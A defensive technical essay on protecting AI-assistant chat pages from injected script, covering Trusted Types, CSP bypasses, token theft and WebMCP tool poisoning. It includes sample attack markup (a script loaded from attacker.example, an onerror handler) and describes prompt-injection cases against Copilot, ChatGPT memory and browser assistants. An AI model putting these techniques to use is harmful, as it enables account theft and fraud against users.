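The best evidence that Trusted Types works comes from Google, which proposed the feature. By July 2021 Google had enforced it on 130 services, and Kotowicz reports that the company had seen no DOM-based XSS in any of them. Google also estimated that Trusted Types could have prevented at least 61% of the confirmed DOM-based flaws that outside researchers had reported to it and that its automatic code checks had missed. The rest came from bugs in sanitisers, the older AngularJS framework, and old code that Google had exempted from the rules.

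Flaws may have gone undetected, and Google had advantages that most sites lack. Its services shared a framework and already used libraries for producing safe HTML. None of the figures concern replies written by a language model.

Microsoft's code editor Visual Studio Code may be a closer comparison, because it also displays Markdown. Its developers found 108 places that broke the Trusted Types rules in nearly a million lines of code. Of these, 75% were trivial to fix without a policy, but the component that displays Markdown needed one. The editor has enforced Trusted Types since January 2021.

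Ordinary developers found Trusted Types much harder. Roth and colleagues ran sessions with 13 participants between July 2022 and April 2023, averaging about 83 minutes each. Ten of the 13 thought less of Trusted Types after trying it. Ten participants completed a standard usability questionnaire, giving the feature an average score of 58.75 out of 100, which the researchers call only marginally acceptable.

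Much of the trouble came from third-party code. Twitter's timeline widget created a frame with no address of its own. The frame inherited the rule requiring Trusted Types but not the site's policy functions, so the widget failed. An advertising widget used `eval()`, and five developers tried to clean its JavaScript with an HTML sanitiser. The sanitiser changed a `<` in the code into `&lt;`, which stopped the code from running.

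The study predates `setHTML()`, and its test page relied heavily on third-party widgets. A chat page with little third-party code should be easier to protect, particularly if it needs to insert only formatted replies.

Adoption of Trusted Types across the web is hard to measure. CentralCSP's *state of the web* cites the HTTP Archive's regular scan of public websites, which found a Content Security Policy on 21.9% of mobile home pages in 2025. Enforcing Trusted Types requires such a policy, so at most 21.9% of those pages enforce it, and the real share is probably much lower. The scan does not sign in, so it misses the account pages where an assistant has the most access.

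### What gets past these defences

A careless policy can meet the browser's requirements without making the page any safer. Roth and colleagues gave later participants a default policy that returned every string unchanged, to help them get started. A site that kept this policy would send the right header and produce few errors, but `innerHTML` would be as dangerous as before.

If a default policy defines the newer function `createParserOptions`, the browser calls it instead of `createHTML` for `innerHTML`. WHATWG warns that a developer who adds `createParserOptions` without specifying a sanitiser loses the cleaning done by `createHTML`.

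Both `setHTML()` and Trusted Types act when a script inserts content in the browser. They don't check HTML that the server has written into the page, so a server that includes saved conversations in its pages has to encode or sanitise them itself.

HTML that contains no script can still cause harm through the page's own code. In DOM clobbering, an element's `id` or `name` replaces a value that the page's code expects. `setHTML()` does not prevent this by default, but a site can configure it to remove both attributes. A script gadget is code in a legitimate library that treats certain elements or attributes as instructions. By default, `setHTML()` removes many of the attributes that such libraries use, but the standard says the list is incomplete and advises developers to check their own libraries.

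Ordinary links and images can also do harm. A link can lead to a fake login page, and an image's address can leak private data, as it could in GitLab's assistant even though it used DOMPurify. `setHTML()` would have removed the image by default, but a site has to allow images if its assistant is meant to show them.

These defences cannot stop a script that is already running in the page from reading the conversation or sending requests, because neither requires an injection sink. The script can also replace the page's sanitising function with one that does nothing. If the site omits the `trusted-types` directive, the script can create its own policy. Google's 2021 rollout omitted the directive and relied on code checks to catch new policies, but those checks would miss code that an attacker adds after they run.

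## Which scripts a Content Security Policy lets run

If a dangerous tag gets past sanitising and Trusted Types, a Content Security Policy (CSP) can still make the browser block the attacker's script before it runs.

A site normally sends its policy as an HTTP header with each page. The policy consists of directives, and the `script-src` directive lists which scripts the browser may run. If the policy has no `script-src`, the browser uses the general list in `default-src`. A policy with neither does not restrict scripts.

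### How the browser decides

W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft of the standard, sets out different checks for different kinds of code.

Inline code is JavaScript written between script tags in the page itself. It has no address for the browser to compare with a list, so under `script-src` the browser refuses it by default. A site can allow it with any of these entries:

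- The keyword `'unsafe-inline'` allows all inline code, including an attacker's.
- A nonce, which is a random value that is new for each page load, allows the script tags that carry it.
- A hash, which is a fingerprint computed from the code, allows only code with exactly that text.

If the list contains a nonce or a hash, the browser ignores `'unsafe-inline'`. Otherwise an attacker could run an injected inline script without a nonce.

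A nonce works only on a script tag, so it cannot allow a `javascript:` address in a link or an event handler such as `onerror` on an image. The browser runs these only if `'unsafe-inline'` is in effect, or if the policy lists the code's hash together with the keyword `'unsafe-hashes'`. W3C advises modern sites against using `'unsafe-hashes'`. If a bank used it to allow its "Transfer" button's handler, an attacker could inject the same code in a script tag, and it would run without anyone pressing the button.

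For a script in an external file, the browser works through these steps:

1. If the script tag carries a nonce from the policy, the browser allows it, whatever the address.
2. If the tag has an `integrity` attribute and the policy lists its hashes, the browser allows the request and then checks that the file matches.
3. If the policy contains `'strict-dynamic'`, the browser refuses any other script tag that it finds while parsing HTML, but allows script elements that running code has created.
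4. In all other cases, the browser compares the address with the hosts in the list.

It repeats the check when the response arrives, in case the server redirected the request to another address.

The browser blocks `eval()` and a few similar functions unless the policy contains `'unsafe-eval'`.

A page can have several policies. A script must satisfy all of them to run, so adding a policy can only tighten the rules.

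### Two policies for the bank's page

Suppose the bank's account page loads one script of its own and a chat widget from `chat.example.net`. A policy based on permitted hosts could be:

```
Content-Security-Policy: script-src 'self' https://chat.example.net;
  object-src 'none'; base-uri 'none'
```

The keyword `'self'` stands for the page's own origin. A policy based on a nonce doesn't need to list any hosts:

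```
Content-Security-Policy: script-src 'nonce-q7Vd…' 'strict-dynamic';
  object-src 'none'; base-uri 'none'
```

The server puts the same random value in its own script tags:

```html
<script nonce="q7Vd…" src="/js/account.js"></script>
<script nonce="q7Vd…" src="https://chat.example.net/widget.js"></script>
```

Suppose the server writes a saved conversation into the page without encoding it, and one of the replies contains an attacker's markup. The attacker doesn't know the nonce, because the server generated it after the attacker wrote the markup.

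| Markup in the reply | Host-list policy | Nonce policy |
|---|---|---|
| `<script>…</script>` | The browser blocks it, because the list has no `'unsafe-inline'`. | The browser blocks it, because the tag has no nonce. |
| `<img src="x" onerror="…">` | The image tag stays, but the browser blocks the handler. | The result is the same. |
| `<script src="https://attacker.example/…">` | The browser blocks it, because the host is not in the list. | The browser blocks it, because the tag has no nonce. |
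| `<script src="https://chat.example.net/…">` | The browser loads the file and runs it. | The browser blocks it, because the tag has no nonce. |

The host list lets the attacker load anything the chat vendor's server will return as script. Adding `'unsafe-inline'` to the host-list policy would also allow the first two attempts, but the browser would ignore that keyword in the nonce policy.

If a script in the page inserts the reply with `innerHTML` instead, browsers do not run script tags in it. Attackers therefore use event handlers, as Positive Security's researcher did at the real bank. Either of the two policies above would have blocked that handler, whatever its name.

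### What a nonce policy needs

A nonce works only if the attacker cannot predict it. W3C requires servers to generate a new nonce each time they send the policy and recommends making it at least 128 bits long. Nonces suit pages that the server builds for each request. Weichselbaum's *Mitigate cross-site scripting (XSS) with a strict Content Security Policy (CSP)* recommends hashes for pages that the server stores and sends unchanged.

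Chat widgets often start as a small loader that adds more scripts, and those scripts don't carry the page's nonce. `'strict-dynamic'` lets them run if permitted code adds them through `createElement()`. The browser still blocks a script tag added through `document.write()`, because that tag goes through the HTML parser, as an injected one would. With `'strict-dynamic'`, the browser also ignores any hosts in the same `script-src` list.

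If an attacker can influence the address from which a permitted script loads another script, `'strict-dynamic'` allows the loaded script to run. W3C therefore advises sites to avoid the keyword when they can, whereas Weichselbaum includes it in the basic recipe.

The other two directives in the example block indirect ways to run scripts. `object-src` controls what the page loads through `object` and `embed` tags. It mattered most when browsers ran Flash, because a Flash file could run JavaScript in the page around it. Browsers have since dropped Flash, and W3C's description of a strict policy no longer includes the directive. Weichselbaum's guide still sets it to `'none'`, which breaks nothing on a page that doesn't use these tags.

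`base-uri` is still essential with nonces. A `base` tag changes the address that a page's relative URLs start from. If an attacker injects one above the bank's first script tag, the browser requests `/js/account.js` from the attacker's server, and the policy allows it because the script tag has a valid nonce. `base-uri` does not fall back to `default-src`, so the site has to set it explicitly.

An attacker may also try to reuse a nonce already in the page by injecting an unfinished script tag just before a real one. The injected tag can then take the real tag's nonce as its own attribute. Under W3C's rules, browsers reject a nonce if the tag shows signs of this, such as a second `<script` among its attributes. One variant gets past the check by repeating an attribute, because the HTML parser discards the repeated one before the browser can inspect it.

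### Why lists of hosts fail

The main evidence against host lists comes from *CSP Is Dead, Long Live CSP!* (Weichselbaum, Spagnuolo and colleagues, 2016). The Google researchers collected 26,011 different policies from the company's search index. They found that an attacker could bypass 94.72% of them, and that 99.34% of hosts with CSP had a policy that gave no benefit against XSS.

Of the 22,425 enforced policies that tried to restrict scripts, 87.63% made the basic mistake of including `'unsafe-inline'` without a nonce. The researchers could still bypass 51.05% of the 2,437 policies without this or similar mistakes, mostly because of a host on the policy's list of allowed sources.

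A common cause was JSONP, an old way of loading data from another origin as a script. The page puts the name of a function in the address, and the server replies with code that passes the data to that function. If an attacker replaces the name with code, a server that doesn't check the name sends that code back as script. The browser runs it because the response came from a permitted host. Error messages that repeat part of the request can cause the same problem, as can uploaded files. A chat vendor that stored visitors' uploads on the same host as its widget could therefore let attackers bypass its customers' policies.

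None of this is by itself a flaw in the permitted site, so the site's owner has little reason to fix it. Of the 15 hosts that policies listed most often, 14 served something the researchers could use to bypass a policy, though two of them only helped if the policy also allowed `eval()`. The median policy listed 12 hosts, and the researchers could bypass 94.8% of policies with lists of that length. The October 2026 attack on ChatGPT later used an endpoint on YouTube.

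In 61% of the JSONP cases, the attacker could only call existing functions, not run arbitrary code. The researchers count this as equally harmful, and on a page with an assistant it could be, if one of those functions sends a chat message. The study also counted policies that were open to Flash, which is no longer a threat, and some of the hosts may have changed since 2016. But its automated checks tested for only a few kinds of bypass, so they missed others.

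Listing an exact file instead of a whole host helps less than it seems to, because after a redirect the browser ignores the path and compares only the host. It does this to avoid revealing where another site sent the user. If a permitted host has an address that redirects to any URL the visitor supplies, an attacker can use it to load other files from the permitted hosts. In *Complex Security Policy*, a history of policies on 10,000 popular sites, Roth, Barron and colleagues found that some lists contained expired or mistyped domains, which an attacker could register and use to serve script.

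Google had tried to maintain a careful list of allowed script sources for Google Maps Activities, an application with four million monthly users. According to Weichselbaum and colleagues, the developers made five major changes to the policy in 2015. The list grew to 15 long addresses and still included a JSONP endpoint. The developers then switched to a nonce with `'strict-dynamic'` and had not needed to change the policy again by the time the study was published.

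### Page code that runs the attacker's text

Nonces stop an attacker from adding a script, but not from using script gadgets in code the page already runs. Weichselbaum and colleagues give the example of a script that reads a function's name from an element in the page and then calls that function. An attacker who can inject that element can choose which function the script calls.

AngularJS evaluates expressions it finds in parts of the page, and it has a mode that does so without `eval()`, so blocking `eval()` does not stop them from running. If the policy allows scripts by host, an attacker can load AngularJS from any permitted host that has a copy, even if the site doesn't use the library. A nonce policy prevents the attacker from loading it, but a page that already runs an old version remains exposed.

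A chat page that displays replies with jQuery's `.html()` function could run an attacker's script tag despite having a correct nonce policy. jQuery is a widely used library, and `.html()` looks like a convenient replacement for `innerHTML`. Unlike `innerHTML`, it takes the script tags out of the HTML and runs them through new script elements. Weichselbaum lists it among the functions that can undo a policy with `'strict-dynamic'`, because under such a policy the browser allows scripts created by a permitted script.

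A nonce can also let injected code run when the server writes the conversation into an inline script as data, so that the chat can display it immediately. The page needs this script, so the server gives it a nonce. If the server doesn't encode the replies for JavaScript, a reply can end the string that contains it and continue as code. The browser applies the nonce to the whole script, so it runs the injected code too.

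### How many sites allow inline code

In *Security*, a chapter of its 2025 report on the state of the web, HTTP Archive found that 21.9% of sites had a Content Security Policy, up from 18.5% a year earlier. Helme (2026), in *Top 1 Million Analysis June 2026*, found policies on 170,057 of the 819,002 popular sites that responded.

| | HTTP Archive, 2025 | Helme, June 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Sites with a policy | 21.9% | 20.8% |
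| Policies counted in the rows below | Those with `script-src` | All |
| `'unsafe-inline'` | 92% | 46.8% |
| `'unsafe-eval'` | 77% | 41.9% |
| A nonce | About 20% | 24.7% |
| `'strict-dynamic'` | About 10% | 1.6% |

The figures for `'unsafe-inline'` differ so much partly because they are percentages of different sets of policies. Invicti's *The dangers of incorrect CSP implementations* (2026) explains that HTTP Archive's 92% covers only policies that use `script-src`. Helme's total also includes policies that only control framing or secure connections. That difference doesn't explain why Helme found more nonces, but the two scans also covered different sites.

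The 92% overstates how many of those policies allow inline code. Google's *Strict CSP* recommends listing `'unsafe-inline'` next to a nonce so that the page still runs in very old browsers that don't support nonces. Newer browsers ignore the keyword when a nonce is present. Even if every policy with a nonce also contains `'unsafe-inline'`, about 72% of the policies in HTTP Archive's group have the keyword and no nonce. A hash or `'strict-dynamic'` would cancel the keyword in some of these, but probably not in most.

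Helme's scan, like HTTP Archive's, does not sign in to sites. Helme notes that many customers of Report URI, the company he founded, use its service only on sensitive pages such as account sections.

Sites keep `'unsafe-inline'` because removing it can break them. Report URI's *10 years of watching the web* argues that keeping it is rational for a team that doesn't know all the inline code its pages run. Often the site's developers didn't write that code. *Web Execution Bundles* (2025) cites a study by Steffens and colleagues in which 86% of sites needed the keyword because scripts in their pages added inline event handlers.

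### Chat widgets that need a looser policy

In *Content Security Policy*, a help page for the ChatBot widget, Lembicz (2022) tells customers to add `'self'` and `'unsafe-inline'` to `script-src` and to allow the vendor's domain.

On a page with a host list, following this advice to add `'unsafe-inline'` would allow injected inline scripts and event handlers everywhere, not just in the chat. This would weaken the site's defence against script injection just as it adds a component that displays text from outsiders. On a page with a nonce, the browser would ignore `'unsafe-inline'`, and any part of the widget that depended on it would fail.

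ChatBot's page is from July 2022 and covers a single vendor's requirements. A widget needs only one nonce on its loader and `'strict-dynamic'` if the loader creates further scripts with `createElement()` and attaches event handlers from JavaScript. For social media buttons, Medley and West recommend using a version that runs in a frame, when such a version exists. If a chat widget also ran in a frame, the host page would not have to allow the vendor's scripts at all.

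### Permitted scripts that turn hostile

When applying `script-src`, the browser checks how a script arrived but doesn't examine what it does. The attackers who altered Awesome Motive's WordPress scripts and hijacked AppsFlyer's domain delivered their code from the usual addresses, so a host list that permitted those addresses would have allowed it. A nonce would also have allowed it, because the site's own script tag loaded the file.

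Subresource Integrity can catch such a change. The site puts the expected hash in the script tag, and the browser refuses a file that doesn't match. HTTP Archive found this feature on 23.6% of mobile pages, mostly for files from content delivery networks. It works well for a fixed version of a library. But as *What Gets Measured Gets Managed* (2025) explains, many third-party scripts change their content or address often, and then the hash would block a legitimate update. A hash on a chat vendor's loader also doesn't cover the scripts the loader adds later under `'strict-dynamic'`.

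Under W3C's draft, a site's policy should not interfere with browser extensions, because the user's choices take priority over the site's. A malicious extension can therefore add script even to a page with the strictest policy.

`script-src` also does not affect prompt injection. The phishing message that Blue41 got a bank's assistant to display contained no code for the browser to block.

### Why a strict policy is still worth having

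W3C describes CSP as a way to limit the damage when other defences fail, not as a replacement for checking input and encoding output. Weichselbaum and colleagues also say that a policy helps only after a developer has made a mistake elsewhere.

Such mistakes are easy to make on a chat page. The nonce policy in the bank example would have blocked all four kinds of markup even though the server had failed to encode the reply. A weak policy fails when the server makes that error, which is when the page needs the policy. The *Content Security Policy Cheat Sheet* from OWASP, a nonprofit security organisation, therefore calls strict policies the leading practice and says they are easier to deploy than host lists.

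Evidence of the effect comes mainly from Google. Weichselbaum and colleagues examined hundreds of XSS flaws in the company's records and expected nonce policies to make a large majority of them harmless. According to Report URI's *Client-Side Security Reporting*, XSS's share of Google's payments to outside researchers for reporting flaws fell from 30% in 2018 to 4.1% in 2023. Report URI, which sells a CSP service, credits the fall to Google's move to CSP, but Google was also introducing Trusted Types in those years. The share could also have fallen because Google paid more for other kinds of flaw.

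A site can combine the two approaches by sending two policies, one that requires a nonce and contains `'strict-dynamic'` and another that lists permitted hosts. An external script then has to satisfy both, so a loader with a valid nonce can bring in more scripts only from approved hosts. If the page has inline scripts, the second policy must allow inline code, which is safe because the first still requires a nonce or hash. The site has to maintain a host list again, but an injected script tag can no longer use a JSONP endpoint on one of those hosts to run code.

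A site can first try out its policy in report-only mode, where the browser can report each violation to an address the site chooses. For an assistant, those reports need to come from signed-in pages with real conversations, since a home page may never load the code that displays a reply. A report can include the first 40 characters of the offending code. W3C warns that developers must encode this text before displaying it, or an attack that failed on the customer's page could run in the report reader's browser.

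## What injected code can do once it runs beside the assistant

An attacker's script that gets past cleaning, Trusted Types and the Content Security Policy runs in the host page with the same powers as the code that draws the chat and sends the user's messages.

*OAuth 2.0 for Browser-Based Applications* (Parecki, De Ryck and Waite), published in August 2026 by the IETF, an internet standards body, describes what injected code can do in web applications generally, though it does not deal with assistants. The code can read the application's variables, call its functions, remove its event listeners and replace functions built into the browser. It can also tamper with most of the application's own defences, because they run in the same page.

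### Reading the conversation

The script can read every message in the chat window from the DOM and have the browser notify it whenever a new one appears. If the server keeps old conversations, the script can retrieve them even when the chat window is empty by sending the same request the page uses to load them. The browser attaches the session cookie, so the server returns the history.

Conversations with the assistant may contain more than the account page does. A bank's customer might have explained why they need a loan or uploaded a letter from their employer. The attacker still has to get the text out of the page, and a site can make that harder by limiting where the page can send data.

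### Sending prompts as the user

An injected script can send the assistant instructions through the chat window. It puts text in the box, triggers the events that normally follow typing, and clicks the send button. The page's own code then builds the request, so the attacker doesn't need to know the request format. The script can also hide the message, which the customer might otherwise see.

Injected code can also send a request straight to the chat server in the format the page uses. This doesn't have to change anything in the chat window, although the message may appear there later if the server saves it in the history.

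An injected script can read the assistant's reply and write the next prompt accordingly. If the model refuses an instruction, the script can rephrase it or start a new conversation and try again. The text in a fake invoice can't adapt this way because it is fixed before the model reads it.

An attacker who can run script on the page may not need the assistant, since the script can request the account balance directly from the bank. The assistant becomes useful to the attacker when its tools can reach something the page cannot, such as a mailbox, or when the server checks the assistant's actions less strictly than the customer's. It can also save the attacker from learning how the site's other functions work.

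### Why these prompts get more trust

An injected script can send the assistant a prompt that arrives as a message from the signed-in customer. When an assistant reads an invoice, the application can label the text as outside content and scan it for hidden instructions, but filters for outside content do not cover the script's prompt. A filter on the customer's own messages has little basis for flagging a request to add a payee, because customers make such requests themselves.

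The security firm ERNW found a way to put text into the user's message without running any script in the chatbot's page. *Vulnerability Disclosure*, published on the firm's blog, Insinuator, in June 2026, describes the AI sidebar in Firefox, which displays a chatbot such as Microsoft's Copilot in a frame. When the user asked for a summary of a web page, Firefox wrote a prompt and pasted it into the chat. The prompt contained the page's title between two markers, then text from the page and an instruction to summarise it.

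A page's owner chooses its title. ERNW created a page whose title imitated the closing marker, so the rest of the title looked like part of the user's request. The rest of the title contained instructions to find a login code in the user's email and fetch a web address containing that code, and Copilot did both. The free version could see only details such as an email's sender and subject, but some sites put the login code in the subject line.

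The user was unlikely to notice, because the browser tab showed only the first few words of the title and the chat window showed only the end of the prompt.

ERNW concludes that chatbot providers probably check emails and web pages closely but accept the user's own prompt as intentional, even if it asks the assistant to send personal data elsewhere. This is an inference, because the report does not compare the result with the same instructions placed in an email or in the body of a page. Mozilla appears to have responded by limiting the title's length, which makes the attack unlikely to work but still leaves outside text in the user's prompt.

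A script running beside an assistant can write the whole prompt and any that follow, whereas ERNW controlled only one field of a prompt that Firefox wrote. Kaya and colleagues found chat plugins that accept conversation history from the browser without checking it. In those plugins, the script can also add messages labelled as the developer's instructions.

### Changing messages on the way

Pages usually send messages with `fetch`, which a script can replace with its own version, as the hijacked AppsFlyer code did. HTTPS does not prevent this, because the script changes a message before the browser encrypts it and the reply after the browser decrypts it.

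Suppose a customer asks the bank's assistant to pay a plumber €240. The replacement function puts the attacker's account number in the request. The assistant asks the customer to confirm a payment to that account, but the function changes the number back to the plumber's before the page displays the question, and the customer confirms. The chat window and the server's log contain different conversations, and neither looks suspicious by itself.

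### Drawing false replies and approval buttons

The script can also display a fake reply without calling the model. It might copy the assistant's style and tell the customer that the session has expired, with a login form underneath. Blue41 had to get a real assistant to write such a message, but a script can display any text the attacker chooses.

Many assistants ask the user to press a button before taking an important action. On a bank's page, an injected script can change the amount shown above the button without changing the payment, or put a button marked "Show statement" on top of the real one. If pressing "Approve" makes the page send a request, the script can often send that request itself, without the customer pressing anything. To be sure that the customer agreed, the bank has to ask somewhere the script cannot reach, such as its phone app.

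### Leaving instructions in memory

Most of these powers last only while the page is open, unless the attacker's markup is stored and runs again on the next visit. But some assistants save facts and preferences about a user and add them to later conversations. If a script gets the assistant to save an instruction, the model may follow it on the user's other devices, and even after the site has fixed the flaw that let the script in.

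Attackers can also alter an assistant's memory without running script. According to Microsoft, they can use links that contain a ready-made prompt, hide text in documents and emails, or trick users into pasting a prompt themselves. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface* (2025) describes a link attack. ChatGPT took text from a link and submitted it as the user's message as soon as the page loaded. In Tenable's example, the text was an instruction to answer only "yes" from then on and to save that in memory.

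OpenAI's fix used the `Sec-Fetch-Site` header, in which the browser records whether a request started on the same site or elsewhere. A server can use the header to detect requests that come from a link on a hostile website, but not those an injected script sends to the page's own origin, because the browser correctly labels them same-origin.

A script in the page can prompt the assistant to save instructions and then delete the assistant's confirmation from the chat window. Repairing the page does not remove the saved instructions, so the site also has to find and delete them.

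### Stealing a token or using the victim's browser

OAuth is a standard way for an application to access a user's data on another service. The application receives an access token, which typically works for minutes or hours. It may also receive a refresh token, which it can exchange for new access tokens over several hours or days. Unless the service ties a token to a particular browser, anyone who copies it can use it from another computer.

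Parecki and colleagues describe four attacks by injected code:

1. The script copies the current tokens and sends them to the attacker.
2. It keeps copying them, so the attacker always has the latest ones. Short lifetimes then help much less.
3. It ignores the existing tokens and opens a hidden frame that starts a new sign-in. If the user still has a session with the login service, the sign-in can finish without any action from the user, and the attacker gets fresh tokens.
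4. It takes no tokens and sends its requests from the victim's browser.

How many of them work depends on where the application keeps its tokens:

| Attack | Page code holds the tokens | A service worker holds them | The site's server holds them |
|---|---|---|---|
| Copying existing tokens, once or repeatedly | Works | Fails | Fails |
| Getting new tokens | Works | Works | Fails |
| Sending requests from the victim's browser | Works | Works | Works |

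A service worker is a script that runs separately from the page and can intercept its requests. The injected script cannot read the worker's memory, but it can cancel the worker's registration, then open a frame that the worker doesn't control and start a new sign-in there.

In the third design, the browser has only a session cookie, and the site's server adds the token to a request before forwarding it. The server must also use its own credentials to request tokens, so an attacker who starts a sign-in in a hidden frame cannot complete it. Parecki and colleagues strongly recommend this design for sensitive applications and any that handle personal data.

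It still leaves the fourth attack, which is enough for the malicious code to read the history, send prompts and approve actions. According to Parecki and colleagues, the application can prevent this attack only by keeping the malicious code from running.

Forcing the attacker to work through the victim's browser limits the damage. The attacker has to act while the page is open and can send only the requests that the browser permits. For instance, a service can refuse requests from scripts on the assistant's origin, even with a valid token. An attacker who has copied the token can avoid this restriction by calling the service from another computer, where the browser's rules don't apply. Routing every request through the site's server also lets the site detect unusual activity and slow it down.

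### Defences inside the page

The HttpOnly setting on a session cookie gives partial protection. If Open WebUI had kept its login token in such a cookie, a script could not have stolen the token, but it could still have sent requests from the open page.

Anti-forgery tokens are designed to stop forged requests from other websites, not requests from a script injected into the bank's own page. A hostile website can make a visitor's browser send the bank a request with the bank's cookie attached, so the bank requires each request to include a secret value that other sites cannot read. In a common version described by Parecki and colleagues, the bank's page code reads the value from a cookie and copies it into a header, and an injected script can do the same.

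Developers sometimes keep a token in a closure, a function with private variables that outside code cannot read. To use the token, the function has to pass it to another function, usually `fetch`. If the attacker has replaced `fetch`, the replacement receives the token as part of the request. Moving the token into a worker avoids this, as long as the worker never sends it back to the page.

A closed shadow root puts the chat's elements in a separate part of the DOM, where other scripts cannot find them through the ordinary DOM functions. This prevents accidental interference and stops a simple script that searches the page for messages. But a script that runs before the chat starts can replace `attachShadow()`, the function that creates the shadow root, and keep a reference to the root. A script that runs later can remove the chat and start it again, or request the history directly from the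 server.

The browser's `isTrusted` property is harder to fake. It is true on an event caused by a real click or key press and false on one that a script created, and scripts cannot change it on a real event object. A chat page could therefore ignore clicks on "Send" that didn't come from the user. But an injected script can wait until the user presses Enter and change the text at that moment, so that a real key press sends the attacker's message. A script can also call the page's sending function directly or send its own request to the server. The server never receives the event object, so it can rely only on what the page reports about how the request began.

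Obfuscation scrambles names and structure in the page's code to make it hard to read, which can slow an attacker down, particularly if the site changes the code often. But the attacker can still open the page on their own computer and watch which requests it sends. Many attacks also don't depend on the scrambled names, since the visible messages are in the DOM and `fetch` has the same name on every site.

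Integrity checks written in JavaScript look for signs of tampering, such as a replaced `fetch` or a new element covering the chat. Checks that run before the attacker's script can keep clean copies of important functions and catch a careless attack. But an attacker's script written for that particular site can turn off the timer that runs the check, or replace the function that reports a problem. If the server expects regular reports that the page is intact, the script can send them itself. Even if the site fully protects its own copy of `fetch`, the script can create an empty frame and take a fresh copy from there.

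These measures slow an attacker down, and some stop attacks written for many sites at once. But none gives the server a reliable way to distinguish the assistant's page code from an attacker's.

### Confining code inside one page

Many of these defences fail because scripts in a page share functions that any of them can change. Conffab's *Hardened JavaScript*, a recorded conference talk, explains that this openness helped the language grow because developers could add missing features themselves. Hardened JavaScript removes much of that openness so that one page can run code from parties that do not trust each other.

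Hardened JavaScript has three main parts. `lockdown()` freezes the language's built-in objects, such as `Array`, so that later code cannot alter them. `harden()` does the same to an object that the site wants to share. A compartment runs code with its own separate global object, which normally provides functions such as `fetch`. Code in a compartment can use only the basic language and whatever the site adds.

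Suppose the bank adds another company's translation tool to its assistant. The bank could run the tool in a compartment and give it one function, which accepts the text of a reply and displays a translation. The tool could not read the account balance or send the text anywhere. MetaMask, a cryptocurrency wallet, confines its plugins with Hardened JavaScript, according to HardenedJS, the project's website.

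Compartments also lack timers and a working clock by default, which makes it harder for code to work out secrets from how long an operation takes. They cannot stop code from freezing the page with an endless loop. To prevent this, the site has to run the code in a separate worker or process.

ShadowRealm, a proposed addition to JavaScript, runs code with its own global object and its own copies of the built-in objects, but without a DOM. Changes to `Array` inside a ShadowRealm therefore do not affect the page. The page and the ShadowRealm can exchange simple values, such as text and numbers, and call each other's functions, but they cannot pass ordinary objects to each other.

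Both approaches require the site to know which code it wants to confine. The site has to run `lockdown()` before any code it distrusts, and load that code into the compartment or ShadowRealm instead of through an ordinary script tag. It also has to decide what the code can access. A chat widget that receives the real `document` object can reach the whole page again, but one that receives too little will not work. The Content Security Policy's ban on `eval()` also blocks code loaded as a string, so the site may have to loosen the policy.

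A site that did all this could isolate a vendor's file that later became malicious, like the WordPress scripts that attackers altered at Awesome Motive. The file would still run, but it couldn't access the page or the administrator's session.

The browser runs injected script from a tag or an event handler in the page, so the script bypasses the site's loader and runs outside every compartment. After `lockdown()`, it can no longer change `Array`, but it can still use or replace the chat window and `fetch`, because these are part of the browser rather than the JavaScript language.

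Putting the assistant in the compartment instead doesn't solve the problem. The assistant would need functions from the page to draw its messages and contact its server, and the attacker's script could tamper with those functions before the assistant received them. A frame from another origin gives the assistant its own document and `fetch`, so sites that want to separate it from injected code use frames.

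### Tools that a page offers through WebMCP

*WebMCP*, a draft standard from the Web Machine Learning Community Group, lets a page offer tools to an assistant in the browser, so injected code can affect an assistant that runs outside the page. The page calls `registerTool()` with a name, a plain-language description, the inputs the tool needs and the JavaScript function to run. The browser adds the tool to the page's list unless the list already has one with the same name, and the page can remove a tool with a signal. The draft has no rule that separates the site's own script from any other script in the page.

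On the bank's page, an injected script could register a tool called `verify_payee` that sends the attacker whatever the assistant enters. It could also register `add_payee` before the bank does, which would make the bank's registration fail. If it ran early enough to replace `registerTool()`, it could change what the bank's tools do without changing their descriptions.

As of April 2026, the draft offered developers no guidance on this, and its security section was only a heading. The group had put its analysis in a separate document, added to the project in late 2025, according to meeting minutes from W3C (2025). Victor Huang of Microsoft wrote the first version. *Privacy and security considerations for WebMCP*, a set of slides by Huang (2025), lists three places where an attacker can put instructions: a tool's description, the result the tool returns, and the input an assistant passes to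 a site.

Huang also assumes that a browser's assistant may know the user's payment details and have information from other websites. Injected script on a clothing shop's page can normally read only the shop's data. But Huang gives the example of a dishonest shop whose dress-finding tool asks for the customer's age, location and pregnancy status as well as their size, and a helpful assistant might fill in all of it. An attacker's script could register the same tool on an honest shop's page.

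Lee, Chang and colleagues (2026), in *WebMCP Tool Surface Poisoning*, tested how assistants respond to tools from a hostile script in the page. They gave GPT-5.4, Claude Opus 4.6 and Gemini 2.5 Flash four tasks, including an online purchase and a driver update. An attack succeeded if the model called the hostile tool, which then sent data from the task to the attacker. The averages for the three models were:

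| What the script did | Attack succeeded | User's task completed |
|---|---|---|
| Registered a hostile tool under a real tool's name first | 100% | 17% |
| Removed a real tool and took its name | 94% | 18% |
| Added a tool whose description told the assistant to call it before a later step | 59% | 81% |
| Hid the same kind of instruction in a 1,203-word description | 36% | 85% |

Taking over a real tool worked almost every time but usually broke the task, which might alert the user. Adding a tool with a persuasive description worked less often, but the user's task usually finished normally. The models differed most when the description was long. Gemini called the added tool in 72% of runs, while Claude never did in 40 attempts.

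A better model is unlikely to solve the first two problems, because the model receives a tool with the right name and nothing in its input shows that another script put it there. The much older GPT-4o and Claude 3.5 Sonnet also failed every time.

Some of the paper's finer results are less certain. In a separate timing test, taking over a tool worked every time if the script finished before the assistant started, but never at three later points. That is hard to reconcile with the main test, where the replacement came during the task and worked in 94% of runs. Lee and colleagues also report that marking a tool as read-only was enough to get the models to call it 87% of the time. The models never called the comparison tool, but it had a more neutral name, which may explain much of the difference. In a broader test, a tool with the same mark succeeded only 6% of the time. All the tests used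 a JavaScript stand-in for WebMCP, not a browser's own version.

Chrome's rules for WebMCP mostly protect a page from other origins. By default, frames from another origin cannot register tools (Chrome for Developers, 2026, introduction to WebMCP). Other sites cannot see or use a page's tools unless the page lists their origins in the `exposedTo` setting (Chrome for Developers, 2026, security guidance), which the standards group agreed on in April (W3C, 2026, minutes). An injected script already has the page's origin, so none of these rules applies to it.

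The same guidance asks developers to mark tools that take consequential actions, such as transferring money, so that the browser or assistant can ask the user first. It also asks them to mark tools that only read data. But whoever registers a tool sets its marks, so an attacker can mark a tool that sends money as read-only. An assistant that skips confirmation for tools marked read-only would then run it without asking the user.

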